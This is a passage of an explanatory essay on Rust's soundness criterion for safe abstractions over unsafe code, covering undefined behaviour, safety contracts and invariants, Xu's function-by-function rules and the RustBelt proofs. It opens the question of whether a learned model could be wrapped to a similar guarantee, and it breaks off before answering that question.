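# Rust's soundness criterion for safe abstractions over unsafe code, and whether a learned model can be wrapped to the same standard

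## Safe Rust, unsafe code and learned models

Rust is a programming language for systems software, such as operating systems, web browsers and game engines, which needs close control over memory. Mozilla sponsored its development, and companies such as Amazon, Dropbox and Cloudflare use it. The older languages for this work, C and C++, give the same control but little protection against misusing it. A C program can read memory it has already given back, or write past the end of a list, and the compiler (the program that translates source code into machine code) usually won't prevent it. *Safe Systems Programming in Rust*, by Jung and colleagues, cites a Microsoft report that 70% of the security vulnerabilities the company fixes are memory errors of this sort.

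Most Rust code is safe Rust, where the compiler rules out such errors. Code marked with the keyword `unsafe` may also use a few operations that the compiler cannot check, and the programmer is responsible for using them correctly. Libraries often use unsafe code internally. Rust programmers call a library's interface sound if no program written purely in safe Rust can use it to break the language's basic rules.

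Machine learning raises a similar problem. Nobody can check a neural network completely, but it is often part of a program that people need to rely on.

### Ownership and borrowing

Every value in Rust has exactly one owner, usually a variable. When execution leaves the block of code that declared the variable, Rust frees the value's memory. Assigning a string to a second variable moves the string, and the compiler rejects any later use of the first variable. Rust's *What Is Ownership?* explains that this prevents the same memory from being freed twice. A string variable holds a pointer to the characters, a length and a capacity. Assignment copies these three values but not the characters, so if both variables stayed usable, Rust would free the same memory once for each. Freeing memory twice can corrupt it, and attackers can sometimes exploit the corruption.

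Moving a value every time a function needs to read it would be tedious, so Rust also lets code borrow a value through a reference, which gives access without taking ownership. A shared reference, written `&v`, normally allows only reading, while a mutable reference, written `&mut v`, also allows changes. According to Rust's *References and Borrowing*, a value can have one mutable reference or any number of shared ones at a given time, but not both. The compiler's borrow checker enforces this rule by working out how long each reference stays in use and rejecting programs in which the uses conflict.

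Four lines are enough to see what the rule prevents:

```rust
let mut scores = vec![70, 85, 90];
let first = &scores[0];
scores.push(95);
println!("{first}");
```

The first line creates a vector, a growable list whose elements sit side by side in one block of memory. The second stores a shared reference to the first element in `first`. The third appends a number. If the block has no room left, the vector has to move to a larger block and free the old one. But `first` would still hold an address in the old block, making it a dangling pointer, and the last line would read memory the program no longer owns.

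The C++ version of this program compiles, but Rust's compiler rejects the Rust version because `push` needs a mutable reference while the shared one is still in use. Rust's *Storing Lists of Values with Vectors* explains a near-identical case and its error message. Swapping the last two lines fixes the program, since nothing then uses `first` after the vector changes. The borrow checker would reject the original order even if the vector had room for another element, because it doesn't check whether the block is full.

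The same rule prevents data races between threads, the parts of a program that run at the same time. A data race happens when two threads access the same memory at once, at least one of them writes, and nothing coordinates them. This cannot happen if data is never both shared and mutable. Java and Go avoid dangling pointers through garbage collection, but Jung and colleagues point out that both languages still permit data races.

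### Undefined behaviour

Undefined behaviour is behaviour that Rust forbids, and once it occurs there is no guarantee about what the program does. The official list, Rust's *Behavior considered undefined*, includes data races, reading through a dangling pointer, and producing an invalid value, such as a true-or-false value stored as something other than 1 or 0. It also includes breaking the aliasing rules, which govern when two pointers may refer to the same memory. The list comes with a warning that it is incomplete and that the exact aliasing rules are not settled.

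A crash is much better than undefined behaviour because it stops the program and makes the failure visible. Undefined behaviour may do neither, since the compiler optimises on the assumption that it never happens.

Google's *Undefined behavior*, a chapter in a guide to unsafe Rust, gives the example of a function that turns a digit character into the corresponding number. For any other character, the function calls `unreachable_unchecked`, which the programmer uses to promise that execution never reaches that point. Computers store the characters 0 to 9 as the numbers 48 to 57, so the compiler may replace ten comparisons with a single subtraction of 48, or keep only the last four binary digits. Both shortcuts are correct for all ten digits.

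If a caller passes the function the letter A, stored as 65, subtraction returns 17, and keeping the last four binary digits returns 1. (Google's text mistakenly gives 15 for the second result, but 65 is 1000001 in binary.) A third permitted translation stops with an error. The source code doesn't determine which of these happens, and the next version of the compiler may produce a different result, so a passing test is weak evidence that the code is free of undefined behaviour.

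Ralf Jung (2021) argues in *Undefined Behavior deserves a better reputation* that undefined behaviour results from a programmer making a false promise to the compiler, rather than from the compiler looking for mistakes to exploit. His example is a function that returns the middle element of a list. Rust normally inserts a bounds check to confirm that the requested position is inside the list. Half the length of a non-empty list is always a valid position, so the check is unnecessary, but the compiler version Jung tried did not remove it. If the programmer promises that the position is valid, the compiler drops the check, but it cannot tell whether the promise is true. Jung considers the ability to make such promises a useful tool, provided programmers have to ask for it explicitly.

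C programmers can make false promises to the compiler without noticing, and the consequences can be serious. In 2009 a function in a Linux network driver read data through a pointer and only afterwards tested whether the pointer was null, meaning that it pointed to nothing. Reading through a null pointer is undefined behaviour in C, so the compiler could treat the pointer as valid from the first read onwards, and it deleted the test as redundant. CIRCL's vulnerability database entry, *CVE-2009-1897* (2009), records that local users could exploit the bug to gain privileges. Wang and colleagues' *A Differential Approach to Undefined Behavior Detection* reports undefined behaviour in many systems, including the Postgres database, with missing security checks as one of the consequences.

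Under Rust's official rules, undefined behaviour anywhere affects the entire program. For example, if a Rust program calls a C function that has undefined behaviour under C's rules, the Rust code loses its guarantees too.

Undefined behaviour is a narrow category. Rust's *What Unsafe Rust Can Do* lists things that the language still counts as safe, including leaking memory, deadlock (threads waiting for each other forever) and deleting the production database. A program that does any of these is probably wrong, but its behaviour still follows from its source code, which is all that Rust's guarantee covers.

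### What unsafe code may do

Inside an unsafe block, a programmer can do five things that safe Rust does not allow:

- read or write through a raw pointer, which is an address without a reference's guarantees;
- call an unsafe function, whose documentation sets conditions that the caller must meet (ordinary C functions fall under this heading);
- read or change a mutable static variable, which is a global variable that several threads might reach at once;
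- implement an unsafe trait, where a trait is a set of abilities that a type can declare, and an unsafe one involves promises that the compiler cannot check;
- read a field of a union, a piece of memory that can hold any of several types with no record of which one is there.

The usual list of things that only unsafe Rust allows has five entries. *Unsafety*, in the Rust language reference, lists eight, adding declaring a block of foreign functions, applying certain attributes, and calling some functions that depend on particular processor features.

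The borrow checker and the type checks still run inside an unsafe block. Brown University's *Unsafe Rust* stresses that a reference in unsafe code faces the same checks as a reference anywhere else. The four-line vector program would fail to compile inside an unsafe block too. Undefined behaviour is still forbidden there, but for the listed operations the programmer becomes responsible for avoiding it.

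### Why Rust needs unsafe code

No automatic check can accept every correct program and reject every faulty one. Rust's compiler rejects programs it cannot verify, including some that would have run correctly.

The standard library function `split_at_mut`, for example, takes a mutable reference to a list and returns two mutable references, one to the part before a given position and one to the rest. Changing both parts is harmless because they don't overlap, but the borrow checker rejects a direct implementation in safe Rust because it treats them as two mutable borrows of the same list. The first version that Brown University presents checks that the position is not past the end of the list, then builds the two halves from raw pointers in an unsafe block. Callers write no unsafe code, which makes the function a safe abstraction, meaning a public interface that safe Rust can call, with unsafe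 code in its implementation.

Some data structures have the same problem. In a doubly linked list, the elements before and after a given element both point to it, so any change to the list touches shared data. Even the vector needs unsafe code, because it reserves memory ahead of time and must track which part it has filled. `Arc` is a pointer type that counts how many users its data has and frees the data when the last one is gone. Its correctness depends on a delicate argument about threads that the compiler cannot reconstruct.

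Other needs for unsafe code come from outside the language. A hardware device may require a program to write to a specific address, and the compiler cannot check that the address is right. Operating systems must do this constantly. Much useful code is also written in C, which the Rust compiler cannot check against Rust's rules.

Jung and colleagues consider two ways Rust could have done without the `unsafe` keyword. The first is to build vectors and reference counting into the language, as Python does. But somebody would still have to implement them, in Python's case in C, and that code is no safer than unsafe Rust. Programmers also could no longer write their own variants, such as the slimmed-down `Arc` that Firefox uses. The second is a type system strong enough to verify `Arc` by itself, which would amount to asking ordinary programmers to work with a theorem prover.

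Steve Klabnik argues in *Does unsafe undermine Rust's guarantees?* that the unsafe keyword does not defeat the purpose of a safe language, because every memory-safe language rests on some code that people have to trust. For example, Ruby programs cannot touch arbitrary memory, but a bug in the Ruby interpreter can still crash them. In his view, what matters is that the trusted code is small and, preferably, marked in the source. That seems right, but it leaves a heavy burden on whoever writes the unsafe code, and Jung and colleagues concede that it is far from obvious how that person can know they have been careful enough.

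### Learned models

A learned model is a component whose behaviour comes from training and not from a written specification. Neural networks are the main example. The input *x* is a list of numbers, such as the brightness of each pixel in an image or codes that stand for pieces of text. The weights *w* are another list of numbers, from a few thousand in a small model to many billions in a large one. A fixed formula *f* combines the two to produce the output *y*:

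*y* = *f*(*x*; *w*)

In a small network the formula might be

*y* = *W*₂ · max(0, *W*₁*x* + *b*₁) + *b*₂

Here *W*₁ and *W*₂ are tables of weights, *b*₁ and *b*₂ are lists of weights, and the max operation replaces every negative number with zero. Larger networks chain many more steps, some more elaborate. Programmers write the formula but not the weights, which come from training. Training usually starts with random weights. It runs the model on many examples, measures how far the outputs are from the desired ones, and adjusts each weight slightly in the direction that reduces the error. It repeats these steps many times.

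Anyone who has a learned model's weights can follow every multiplication and work out the output for a given input. (Language models often choose among possible next words at random, but the random numbers can count as part of the input.) A correctly written implementation gives every input a definite result, so this is not undefined behaviour in Rust's sense. But nobody has a short statement of which outputs the model gives on which inputs.

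The specification for a sorting function is that the output contains the same items as the input and no item is smaller than the one before it. This covers every possible list, and somebody could write it down before the program existed and then check the program against it.

A network that reads handwritten digits from greyscale images of 28 by 28 pixels should answer 7 when the image shows a 7. But nobody has a formal definition of which grids of 784 numbers show a 7, which is largely why people train a network for the job. The formula and the weights describe the network's actual behaviour exactly, but that description is just the model again. It gives answers one image at a time, and with 256 levels of brightness per pixel there are 256⁷⁸⁴ possible images, or roughly 10¹⁸⁸⁸. Tests cover a vanishing fraction of them. Training doesn't guarantee correct answers on the rest, because it only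 reduces error on the examples it uses.

A learned model's behaviour can still be partly specified. For example, the digit network always returns ten numbers, one for each digit, and this follows from its formula whatever the weights are. The behaviour cannot be fully specified in the sense that such facts, even taken together, fall well short of determining whether the model's answers are right.

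Rust programmers can put code that the compiler cannot check behind an interface and guarantee that no safe program can use that interface to cause undefined behaviour. Can they also put a learned model behind ordinary code and guarantee that a named event never happens, whatever the model outputs?

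## What the soundness criterion requires

Rust's reference manual calls unsafe code sound if no safe client can use it to cause undefined behaviour. A safe client is any program that uses a library's public interface and contains no unsafe code of its own. For a whole library *L*, the definition reads:

A library *L* is sound if and only if no run of any safe client *C* together with *L* has undefined behaviour.

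In symbols:

Sound(*L*) ⇔ ∀*C* ∈ SafeClients(*L*), ∀*r* ∈ Runs(*C* + *L*): ¬UB(*r*)

"Every safe client" includes programs not yet written and programs written by careless or hostile people. "Every run" includes every input and every way threads might interleave. A single bad run of a single client makes a library unsound, so good runs alone can't show that it is sound, however many there are.

A client also has to compile, which rules out many programs. For example, a client can't pass a string to a function that accepts only a Boolean. Library authors can therefore often make an interface sound by choosing its types well, without run-time checks.

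Almost every client also uses other libraries that contain unsafe code, starting with Rust's standard library. *A Trace-based Approach for Code Safety Analysis* (Xu, 2025) allows these only if they are sound themselves. Without that condition, every library would count as unsound, since a client could always combine it with an unsound one. It is harder to determine whether two libraries that are sound separately are also sound together, and formal proofs of soundness have to address this. The definition also assumes a correct compiler and working hardware.

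### Unsound code that nobody misuses

Tolnay (2019), in *Soundness bugs in Rust libraries*, imagines a C function called `frob` that takes a whole number and corrupts memory if the number is 10. Here are three ways a Rust library could offer it, with `ffi::frob` standing for the C function:

```rust
pub fn frob_checked(arg: i32) {
    assert!(arg != 10);
    unsafe { ffi::frob(arg) }
}

/// Safety: `arg` must not be 10.
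pub unsafe fn frob_unchecked(arg: i32) {
    unsafe { ffi::frob(arg) }
}

pub fn frob_plain(arg: i32) {
    unsafe { ffi::frob(arg) }
}
```

`frob_checked` is sound, because the assertion stops the program before a 10 can reach the C function. `frob_unchecked` passes everything through, but it is marked `unsafe`, so safe code cannot call it. `frob_plain` is unsound, because safe code can call `frob_plain(10)` and corrupt memory. Adding a comment that callers must avoid 10 wouldn't make it sound, because the compiler doesn't enforce comments.

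Tolnay also gives a version with no run-time check. If only four settings make sense, the library can define a type with four values, numbered 0 to 3, and accept only that type. A client that passes 10 then fails to compile.

If a company's code contains only one call to the library, `frob_plain(0)`, the program has no undefined behaviour and an attacker gains nothing from `frob`. The library is still unsound, because soundness is a property of the interface, not of its current callers.

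Unsound interfaces often exist without any code misusing them, at least in the code Tolnay reviewed. His employer had more than 500,000 lines of Rust, about 99.7% of it safe. He examined around 60 of its nearly 1,200 unsafe blocks and found three soundness bugs, plus a fourth in a separate codebase called Libra. No existing code misused the faulty interface in any of the four cases. The sample is small and comes from one reviewer, but it shows why programmers distinguish "unsound" from "vulnerable".

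People who agree on the definition of soundness disagree about how urgent such bugs are. Tolnay thinks a company that can inspect every caller may reasonably postpone a fix, although misuse becomes inevitable as the number of users grows. For a public library, whose maintainer can't see the callers, he would treat any unsoundness as a serious vulnerability. Microsoft's *Safety Guidelines* allow no exceptions, even where undefined behaviour is only a remote possibility and would take strange code to trigger.

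### Safety contracts

Some functions cannot prevent misuse as `frob_checked` does. For example, a function that reads from an arbitrary address cannot check whether the address is valid. Its author must mark it `unsafe` and document a safety contract, the conditions that a caller must meet.

The compiler checks only that the call appears in unsafe code, not that it meets the contract. *Unsafe in Rust* explains that the programmer who writes an unsafe block is responsible for meeting the conditions, while marking a function unsafe passes some of that responsibility to its callers.

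Xu extends the definition of soundness to these functions. An unsafe function *f* with contract *K* is sound if and only if, for every program *P* that calls *f* and has no other unsafe code,

*P* meets *K* ⇒ *P* has no undefined behaviour.

A safe function is then simply one with an empty contract, which every program meets.

An unsafe function can therefore be unsound too, if its contract omits a necessary condition. The Rust Project's *Improving Unsafe Code Documentation in the Rust Standard Library* gives the example of a function that takes a value of any type and reads its first four bytes as a number. The contract requires the value to have at least four bytes, with no unused gaps among them. But Rust also requires the address being read to be suitably aligned, which usually means divisible by four. A caller who passes an array of four single bytes meets both written conditions and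 may still cause undefined behaviour. The function's author is at fault for not listing alignment as a third condition.

Omissions like this also occur in practice. The same document links to several cases in which the standard library's own safety documentation was missing or incomplete.

### Splitting a list, line by line

The function `split_at_mut`, which divides a list into two parts that the caller can change independently, shows how an author meets the contracts of unsafe functions inside a safe one. A simplified version looks like this:

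```rust
pub fn split_at_mut<T>(list: &mut [T], mid: usize) -> (&mut [T], &mut [T]) {
    let len = list.len();
    assert!(mid <= len);
    let rest = len - mid;
    let start = list.as_mut_ptr();
    unsafe {
        let left = from_raw_parts_mut(start, mid);
        let right = from_raw_parts_mut(start.add(mid), rest);
        (left, right)
    }
}
```

Take a list of five elements, at positions 0 to 4, with `mid` equal to 2.

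Much of the argument follows from the first line. Because `list` is a mutable reference, the function starts with exclusive access to five initialised elements that sit side by side in memory. The return type lets Rust tie both returned references to the original borrow, so the caller cannot access the original list while either part is still in use.

The next two lines read the length and stop the program if `mid` is too large. A `mid` of 5 would correctly pass, because the right part would then be empty. The subtraction sets `rest` to 3, and the assertion guarantees that the result is never negative. `as_mut_ptr` then returns the address of the first element as a raw pointer, which safe code may obtain but not dereference.

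Inside the unsafe block, `from_raw_parts_mut` turns an address and a count into a mutable reference. Its contract requires, roughly, that the address be the start of that many initialised elements in one block of memory, and that nothing else access them while the reference is in use. `start.add(mid)` moves the address forward by two elements, which is allowed because the result stays within the list (or, when `mid` equals `len`, lands at its end). `left` covers positions 0 and 1, and `right` covers positions 2, 3 and 4. The two parts don't overlap and together cover the list exactly, so both calls meet the contract.

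Most of this argument concerns lines outside the unsafe block. Paharia (2026), in *iddqd, or the hardest kind of unsafe Rust*, points out that a small change to one of those lines, such as adding 1 to `rest`, makes the function unsound, because the right part would then include position 5, which is outside the list.

The Rust Project's *Working with Unsafe* has a similar example, a function that checks that a position is less than the length and then returns the element at that position. Changing `<` to `<=` makes the function unsound, because a list of five elements has nothing at position 5. But `<=` is correct in `split_at_mut`, so a reviewer can't judge the comparison without working out what the unsafe code below it needs.

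### A vector and its module

Everything relevant to `split_at_mut` is inside a single function. A vector is harder to check because its functions rely on data that other functions wrote, perhaps much earlier. Here is a simplified vector with a method that looks up an element:

```rust
pub struct Vector<T> {
    ptr: *mut T,   // start of the block of memory
    cap: usize,    // how many elements the block can hold
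    len: usize,    // how many it holds now
}

impl<T> Vector<T> {
    pub fn get(&self, i: usize) -> Option<&T> {
        if i < self.len {
            Some(unsafe { &*self.ptr.add(i) })
        } else {
            None
        }
    }
}
```

`get` returns a reference to element `i`, or `None` if there is no such element. Its check, `i < self.len`, resembles the assertion in `split_at_mut`, but it reliably prevents invalid accesses only if `len` is correct. So `get` depends on a safety invariant, a fact about the vector's data that the surrounding code has to maintain: `ptr` points to a block with room for `cap` elements, `len` is at most `cap`, and the first `len` places hold initialised elements.

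In *The Scope of Unsafe* (2016), Ralf Jung breaks this invariant with a function called `evil`, whose body is `self.len += 2`. Calling `evil` on a three-element vector sets `len` to 5, and `get(4)` then reads memory that may hold no element or may not belong to the vector. `evil` contains no unsafe code, and the compiler accepts it because adding 2 to an integer is ordinarily harmless.

Jung then defines a second type with the same three fields and the same `evil` function, but no other functions. In this type `evil` is harmless, because no code relies on `len` being correct. The compiler treats the two type definitions identically. Whether `evil` is harmful depends on what the rest of the module does with the fields, so reviewing the unsafe blocks alone is not enough.

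*Working with Unsafe* does the same with the capacity by adding a function, `make_room`, that increases `cap` by one without obtaining more memory. Suppose a vector has room for four elements and is full. After `make_room`, `cap` is 5. The next call to `push` compares `len` with `cap` and, because they differ, writes a fifth element past the end of the block. `push` cannot detect the error, since `cap` is its only record of the block's size.

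To check the invariant, a reviewer has to read only the vector's module (a named section of a program, often a single file). In Rust, a field is private to its module unless the programmer makes it public. Code outside the vector's module therefore cannot write `v.len = 1000`, and only functions inside the module can break the invariant. If `len` were public, a safe client could set it to 1000 and call `get(999)`, and the vector would be unsound however carefully its author had written the rest.

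Private functions are less restricted. The Rust Project notes that `make_room` does no harm if it stays private, since no client can call it. The author only has to make sure that no public function uses it in a way that lets a client access a broken vector.

The standard library's vector has an unsafe method, `set_len`, that lets callers set the length directly. Its body contains no unsafe operation, so the compiler would have accepted it as a safe function, and the library's developers had to remember to mark it unsafe. An accepted Rust Project proposal would let programmers put `unsafe` on a field such as `len`, and the compiler would then require an unsafe block wherever code might break the field's invariant. According to the Rust Project's *Stabilize Unsafe Fields*, a preliminary implementation exists, but gaps in the supporting tools still prevent wide use.

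### Invariants for the compiler and for the library

A vector's invariant can't hold at every moment, because the vector grows by switching to a larger block and then recording the new capacity. Between these steps, it holds the new block's address but the old block's capacity.

Jung's *Two Kinds of Invariants* (2018) explains why this is allowed. A safety invariant has to hold whenever safe code outside the library can access the data. While `push` is running, no other code can see the half-updated vector, and by the time `push` returns, the fields are consistent again.

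A validity invariant is stricter. It describes which values of a type are legal at all, and the compiler relies on it everywhere, including inside unsafe code. For example, a `bool` must be stored as 0 or 1, which leaves 254 spare values in its byte. `Option<bool>`, which holds true, false or nothing, also fits in one byte because the compiler can use a spare value for "nothing". Storing any of those 254 values in a `bool` is undefined behaviour immediately, even if the next line would have corrected it.

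Rust's text type has both kinds of invariant. Its validity invariant is that its bytes are initialised, and its safety invariant is that they form correct UTF-8, the standard encoding for text. Unsafe code that briefly holds badly encoded text has not yet caused undefined behaviour, but it might if it passes the text to a function that relies on the encoding.

The two also differ in how easily a program can check them. Testing whether a byte is 0 or 1 is trivial. But if a variable holds a function from booleans to numbers, its safety invariant requires that calling the function never causes undefined behaviour. Jung observes that checking this would mean solving the halting problem, which no program can do in general.

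Jung later regretted the names. Jung (2024), *Stabilize having the concept of "validity invariant" and "safety invariant"*, proposes "language invariant" and "library invariant" instead, to match the terms "language UB" and "library UB" (UB is undefined behaviour). Another participant in the discussion objected that the term "library UB" has led people to believe that some undefined behaviour is acceptable.

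### What a sound library can still get wrong

Soundness rules out only undefined behaviour. A version of `get` that returned the first element of the vector whatever position the caller asked for, and `None` if the vector was empty, would be useless but sound. A version that always stopped the program with an error (a panic), or one that never returned, would also be sound.

Rustmax's *Behavior not considered unsafe*, a copy of a chapter from Rust's reference, adds integer overflow to the deadlocks and leaks that the criterion permits. Overflow happens when a calculation produces a number too large for its type. Rust then either panics or wraps the number around to the other end of the type's range, depending on the build settings. Both behaviors are well defined, though the wrapped number may be wrong.

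The chapter also covers logic errors. A hash map computes where to store each item from the item's key, so equal keys must lead to the same place. If a programmer supplies keys that break this rule, the map may lose items, return wrong results, panic or run forever, but the map's author must ensure that it doesn't cause undefined behaviour.

A sound function can also cause harm when it works as intended. Microsoft's guidelines give `delete_database()` as an example of a function that is dangerous to call but should not be marked `unsafe`, because `unsafe` is reserved for the risk of undefined behaviour. If authors marked every dangerous function `unsafe`, programmers would see the marker so often that they would stop paying attention to it.

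The criterion is narrow partly for practical reasons. According to the Rust Project's *what unsafe does*, the problems that Rust leaves out are impractical to rule out completely. Undefined behaviour is defined the same way for every program, but what counts as a right answer depends on what a particular program is for.

### Who is to blame

When a program has undefined behaviour, the criterion determines whose code needs fixing. If the client contains no unsafe code, the fault is in a library (or, occasionally, in the compiler), however odd the client is and even if its author ignored the documentation. If the client called an unsafe function and broke its contract, the client is at fault. If the client met the contract, the function's author is at fault, either for a mistake in the code or for leaving a condition out of the contract.

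The criterion requires library authors to defend against clients that no sensible person would write, which can seem harsh. Paharia gives two reasons for accepting this. Code that withstands deliberate abuse also withstands honest mistakes, and a firm rule makes it easier to decide who is responsible for preventing undefined behaviour. If the rule covered only reasonable clients, people would argue about what was reasonable each time something went wrong.

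The criterion treats a module as a unit, so it doesn't settle which code inside the module is at fault. Some programmers might blame the unsafe code in `get` rather than `evil`, because without it a wrong length would be harmless. Jung agrees that the wrong length would then be harmless, but he still blames `evil`. Rewriting the unsafe code to tolerate a wrong length would defeat the purpose of having a vector, so anyone repairing the vector would delete `evil` instead. The safety invariant justifies blaming `evil`, so it helps a great deal if the module's author has written the invariant down.

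### Turning the definition into rules

The definition states what a safe abstraction must achieve but not how to achieve it. *Safety, threadsafety*, a guide to Rust, warns that anyone writing a library with a complicated interface will have to deal with soundness "largely unaided". A draft Rust Safety Standard, posted for comment as *Pre-RFC*, criticizes the definition for giving no actionable guidance on which functions to mark unsafe. The Rust Project accepted work on an experimental standard as one of its goals for 2026, on the grounds that its existing guidelines are not detailed enough.

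The draft builds on Xu's trace-based account, which starts from the unsafe operations and traces the conditions in their contracts outwards through the calling functions. The function containing an unsafe operation must either meet that operation's conditions or pass the unmet ones on to its own callers. If a safe public function still relies on its callers to meet a condition, the library is unsound.

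For types with a safety invariant, Xu adds two main rules:

- A function that creates a value must establish the invariant, provided the caller meets the function's own contract.
- A method that receives a value satisfying the invariant must leave it satisfied, and must meet the contracts of all the unsafe operations it performs, again provided the caller meets the method's contract.

Together these rules give an argument by induction. A new, empty vector has length and capacity zero, which satisfies the invariant. `push` preserves it, and so does `get`, which changes nothing. The vector therefore satisfies the invariant each time `get` runs, regardless of how many calls a client makes or in what order. `evil` breaks the second rule, so a reviewer can reject it without imagining any particular client. This improves on the bare definition by replacing a question about infinitely many programs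 with a separate question about each function.

The rules are stricter than the definition about `make_room`, which breaks the invariant and would have to be marked unsafe even as a private function. A reader of the draft also spotted a case where the rules are too lenient. The draft has a separate rule for free functions (those outside any type), which lets them be safe if they contain no unsafe code. But a free function in the vector's module can still assign to `len`, because private fields are accessible throughout the module. A safe client could use such a function to set a false length and then call `get`. Applying the rules for methods to every function that can access the private fields would close the gap.

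A longer dispute concerned a type called `EvenNumber`, which is supposed to hold an even number, and whether a function that creates one without checking must be marked unsafe. According to the Rust Project, the type's author must first decide whether evenness is a safety invariant. If it is, the function must be unsafe. If it isn't, the function can be safe, but no unsafe code may rely on the number being even.

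A post in *Private unsafe fields are a poorly motivated feature* compares marking the function unsafe with leaving it safe when no unsafe code relies on such a fact yet. Marking it unsafe burdens users now but lets the author rely on the fact later. Leaving it safe is easier for users, but the author can't later rely on the fact for safety without releasing a new major version. Microsoft's guidelines seem to rule out marking it unsafe, at least until misuse could lead to undefined behaviour.

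These rules don't resolve another complaint, that the definition depends on an incomplete list of undefined behaviours. According to Rust's reference, the list may grow or shrink, and there is not yet a formal model of what unsafe code may do. If the list grows, a sound library can become unsound without any change to its code. Xu's account has the same weakness because it assumes that every unsafe operation has a complete contract, which nobody can write while the list is incomplete.

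Jung suggests starting with strict validity invariants and relaxing them later. Accepting more values as valid can only turn undefined behaviour into defined behaviour, so code that was correct under the stricter rule stays correct. For example, Rust has not settled whether a reference must always point to a valid value, but code that treats this as a requirement will be safe either way. Changing a safety invariant in either direction, however, can break existing code. If the library loosens one, code that relies on it may break, and if the library tightens one, code that produces the data may no longer satisfy it.

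## How soundness is proved, tested and lost

Xu's rules turn soundness into a separate check on each function, but the argument behind them is informal. It assumes that safe code can affect a vector only through the vector's own functions, and that the vector stays sound when a client combines it with threads, locks and other people's libraries. In *RustBelt*, Jung, Jourdan and colleagues (2018) turned these assumptions into theorems. They proved the safety of λRust, a small language with Rust's ownership, borrowing and lifetimes (the periods during which references stay usable). They also proved the safety of several real libraries that contain unsafe code. Coq, a proof checker, verified every step.

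### Types as predicates

The traditional way to prove a language safe is to show that every program the type checker accepts runs without undefined behaviour. That doesn't help with unsafe code, whose safety the type checker can't verify. *Safe Systems Programming in Rust* gives a small example, a program that would crash if it took one branch of an `if`, but always takes the other. The program is safe, but the typing rules reject it. The same is true of larger code such as `Arc` and `Vec`.

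RustBelt therefore defines a type by what must be true of its data. Each type τ has a predicate

⟦τ⟧.own(*t*, *v*)

which holds if thread *t* owns the data *v* and *v* is a proper value of type τ. For `bool`, this just means that *v* is 0 or 1. For `Box<T>`, a pointer that has sole ownership of a value of type `T`, the predicate is roughly

⟦Box<T>⟧.own(*t*, *v*) = ∃ℓ, *w*: (*v* = ℓ) ∗ (ℓ ↦ *w*) ∗ ⟦T⟧.own(*t*, *w*)

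In words, *v* is an address ℓ, the memory at ℓ holds some data *w*, and *w* is a valid value of type `T`. The arrow also stands for the exclusive right to use that memory. The star is a separating conjunction, an "and" whose two sides must describe separate memory. If a thread owns two boxes, the star guarantees that they have different addresses, so freeing one cannot damage the other.

Mutable references are harder to describe because they confer ownership only temporarily. RustBelt splits this ownership in time. The reference gets access to the memory until a given lifetime ends, and the original owner keeps a guarantee of getting the memory back afterwards. Code that uses the reference may briefly violate the predicate, as `push` does, but must restore it before finishing.

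A function from type A to type B meets its specification if, given any argument that satisfies A's predicate, it runs without undefined behaviour and any result it returns satisfies B's predicate. A function that never returns therefore meets its specification if it has no undefined behaviour, which is consistent with the soundness criterion, since that also allows useless but harmless code.

### An index that stays inside its slice

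A slice is a view of elements that sit side by side in memory. The type below stores a slice together with a position that always lies inside it:

```rust
pub struct Cursor<'a, T> {
    slice: &'a [T],
    pos: usize,
}

impl<'a, T> Cursor<'a, T> {
    pub fn new(slice: &'a [T], pos: usize) -> Option<Self> {
        if pos < slice.len() { Some(Cursor { slice, pos }) } else { None }
    }
    pub fn get(&self) -> &'a T {
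        unsafe { self.slice.get_unchecked(self.pos) }
    }
    pub fn advance(&mut self) {
        if self.pos + 1 < self.slice.len() { self.pos += 1; }
    }
}
```

`'a` is the lifetime of the borrowed slice. `get_unchecked` reads an element without a bounds check, so the caller must ensure that the index is inside the slice.

To the compiler, a `Cursor` is any slice reference plus any whole number. Whoever writes the proof chooses a stronger predicate, for a cursor with slice *s* and position *i*:

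⟦Cursor<'a, T>⟧.own(*t*, (*s*, *i*)) = ⟦&'a [T]⟧.own(*t*, *s*) ∗ (*i* < len(*s*))

The last part is the safety invariant. Predicates like this one also distinguish Jung's two vector types, which have identical fields, because only the real vector's predicate restricts `len`.

Each function now needs a short proof. `new` receives a valid slice and an arbitrary number, and builds a cursor only after checking that the number is less than the slice's length, so the cursor satisfies the predicate. The proof for `get` can assume that its cursor satisfies the predicate, so *i* < len(*s*), which is the condition `get_unchecked` requires. The element `get` returns belongs to the slice, so it stays available for the lifetime `'a`, as the return type requires. `advance` borrows a cursor that satisfies the predicate and must preserve it, which it does by checking the new position before storing it.

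Like `evil`, a method that added an arbitrary number to `pos` would compile, but its proof would fail because the new position might not be less than the length.

Now take a client:

```rust
let marks = [70, 85, 90];
if let Some(mut c) = Cursor::new(&marks, 1) {
    c.advance();
    println!("{}", c.get());
}
```

This program needs no proof of its own. Jung and colleagues proved a lemma for every typing rule in λRust, such as the rule for assigning through a mutable reference. Each lemma states that if the predicates for the rule's inputs hold before a step, the step has no undefined behaviour and the predicates for its outputs hold afterwards. The type checker accepts a client by applying the rules one after another, so the corresponding lemmas together cover the whole program. The client can't access `pos` directly, so it can only change a cursor through functions that already have proofs.

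A program is therefore safe if all its unsafe code is in libraries verified in this way. Adding another verified library doesn't invalidate the existing proofs.

### Two libraries that were unsound together

The proofs can be combined only if they all make the same assumptions about what safe code can do. In April 2015, a few weeks before releasing Rust 1.0, Rust's developers discovered how much this matters.

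The standard library then had a function, `thread::scoped`, that started a thread and let it borrow local variables from the calling function. The calling function might return, destroying those variables, while the thread was still reading them. To prevent this, `thread::scoped` returned a guard whose destructor, the code Rust runs when a value is destroyed, waited for the thread to finish.

The library also had `Rc`, a simpler version of `Arc` for use within one thread. If two `Rc` values point to each other, their counts of users never reach zero, so their destructors never run. Usually this only wastes memory. But a safe client could put a thread's guard inside such a cycle. The function then returned without waiting for the thread, which went on reading memory that the program had already reused.

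Taken separately, `thread::scoped` was sound if destructors always ran in time, and `Rc` was sound if safe code was allowed to leak. The developers needed one assumption for the whole language, and they chose to allow leaks. They withdrew `thread::scoped` and made `mem::forget`, which discards a value without running its destructor, a safe function. The current replacement, `thread::scope`, has been in the standard library since 2022. It takes the client's code as an argument, runs it, and waits for all the threads to finish before returning, so the client has no guard to leak.

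RustBelt's logic incorporates this choice by letting a proof discard ownership at any point. `Rc` is sound under that rule, but the old scoped threads were not.

Existing proofs can also fail to carry over when the predicates change. In *RustHornBelt*, Matsushita, Denis and colleagues (2022) extended RustBelt's model to prove that functions return the right results as well as being safe. They verified `Vec`, `Cell` and `Mutex` (a lock), but a technical obstacle kept them from covering `Rc`, `Arc` and two other types that RustBelt had already proved safe.

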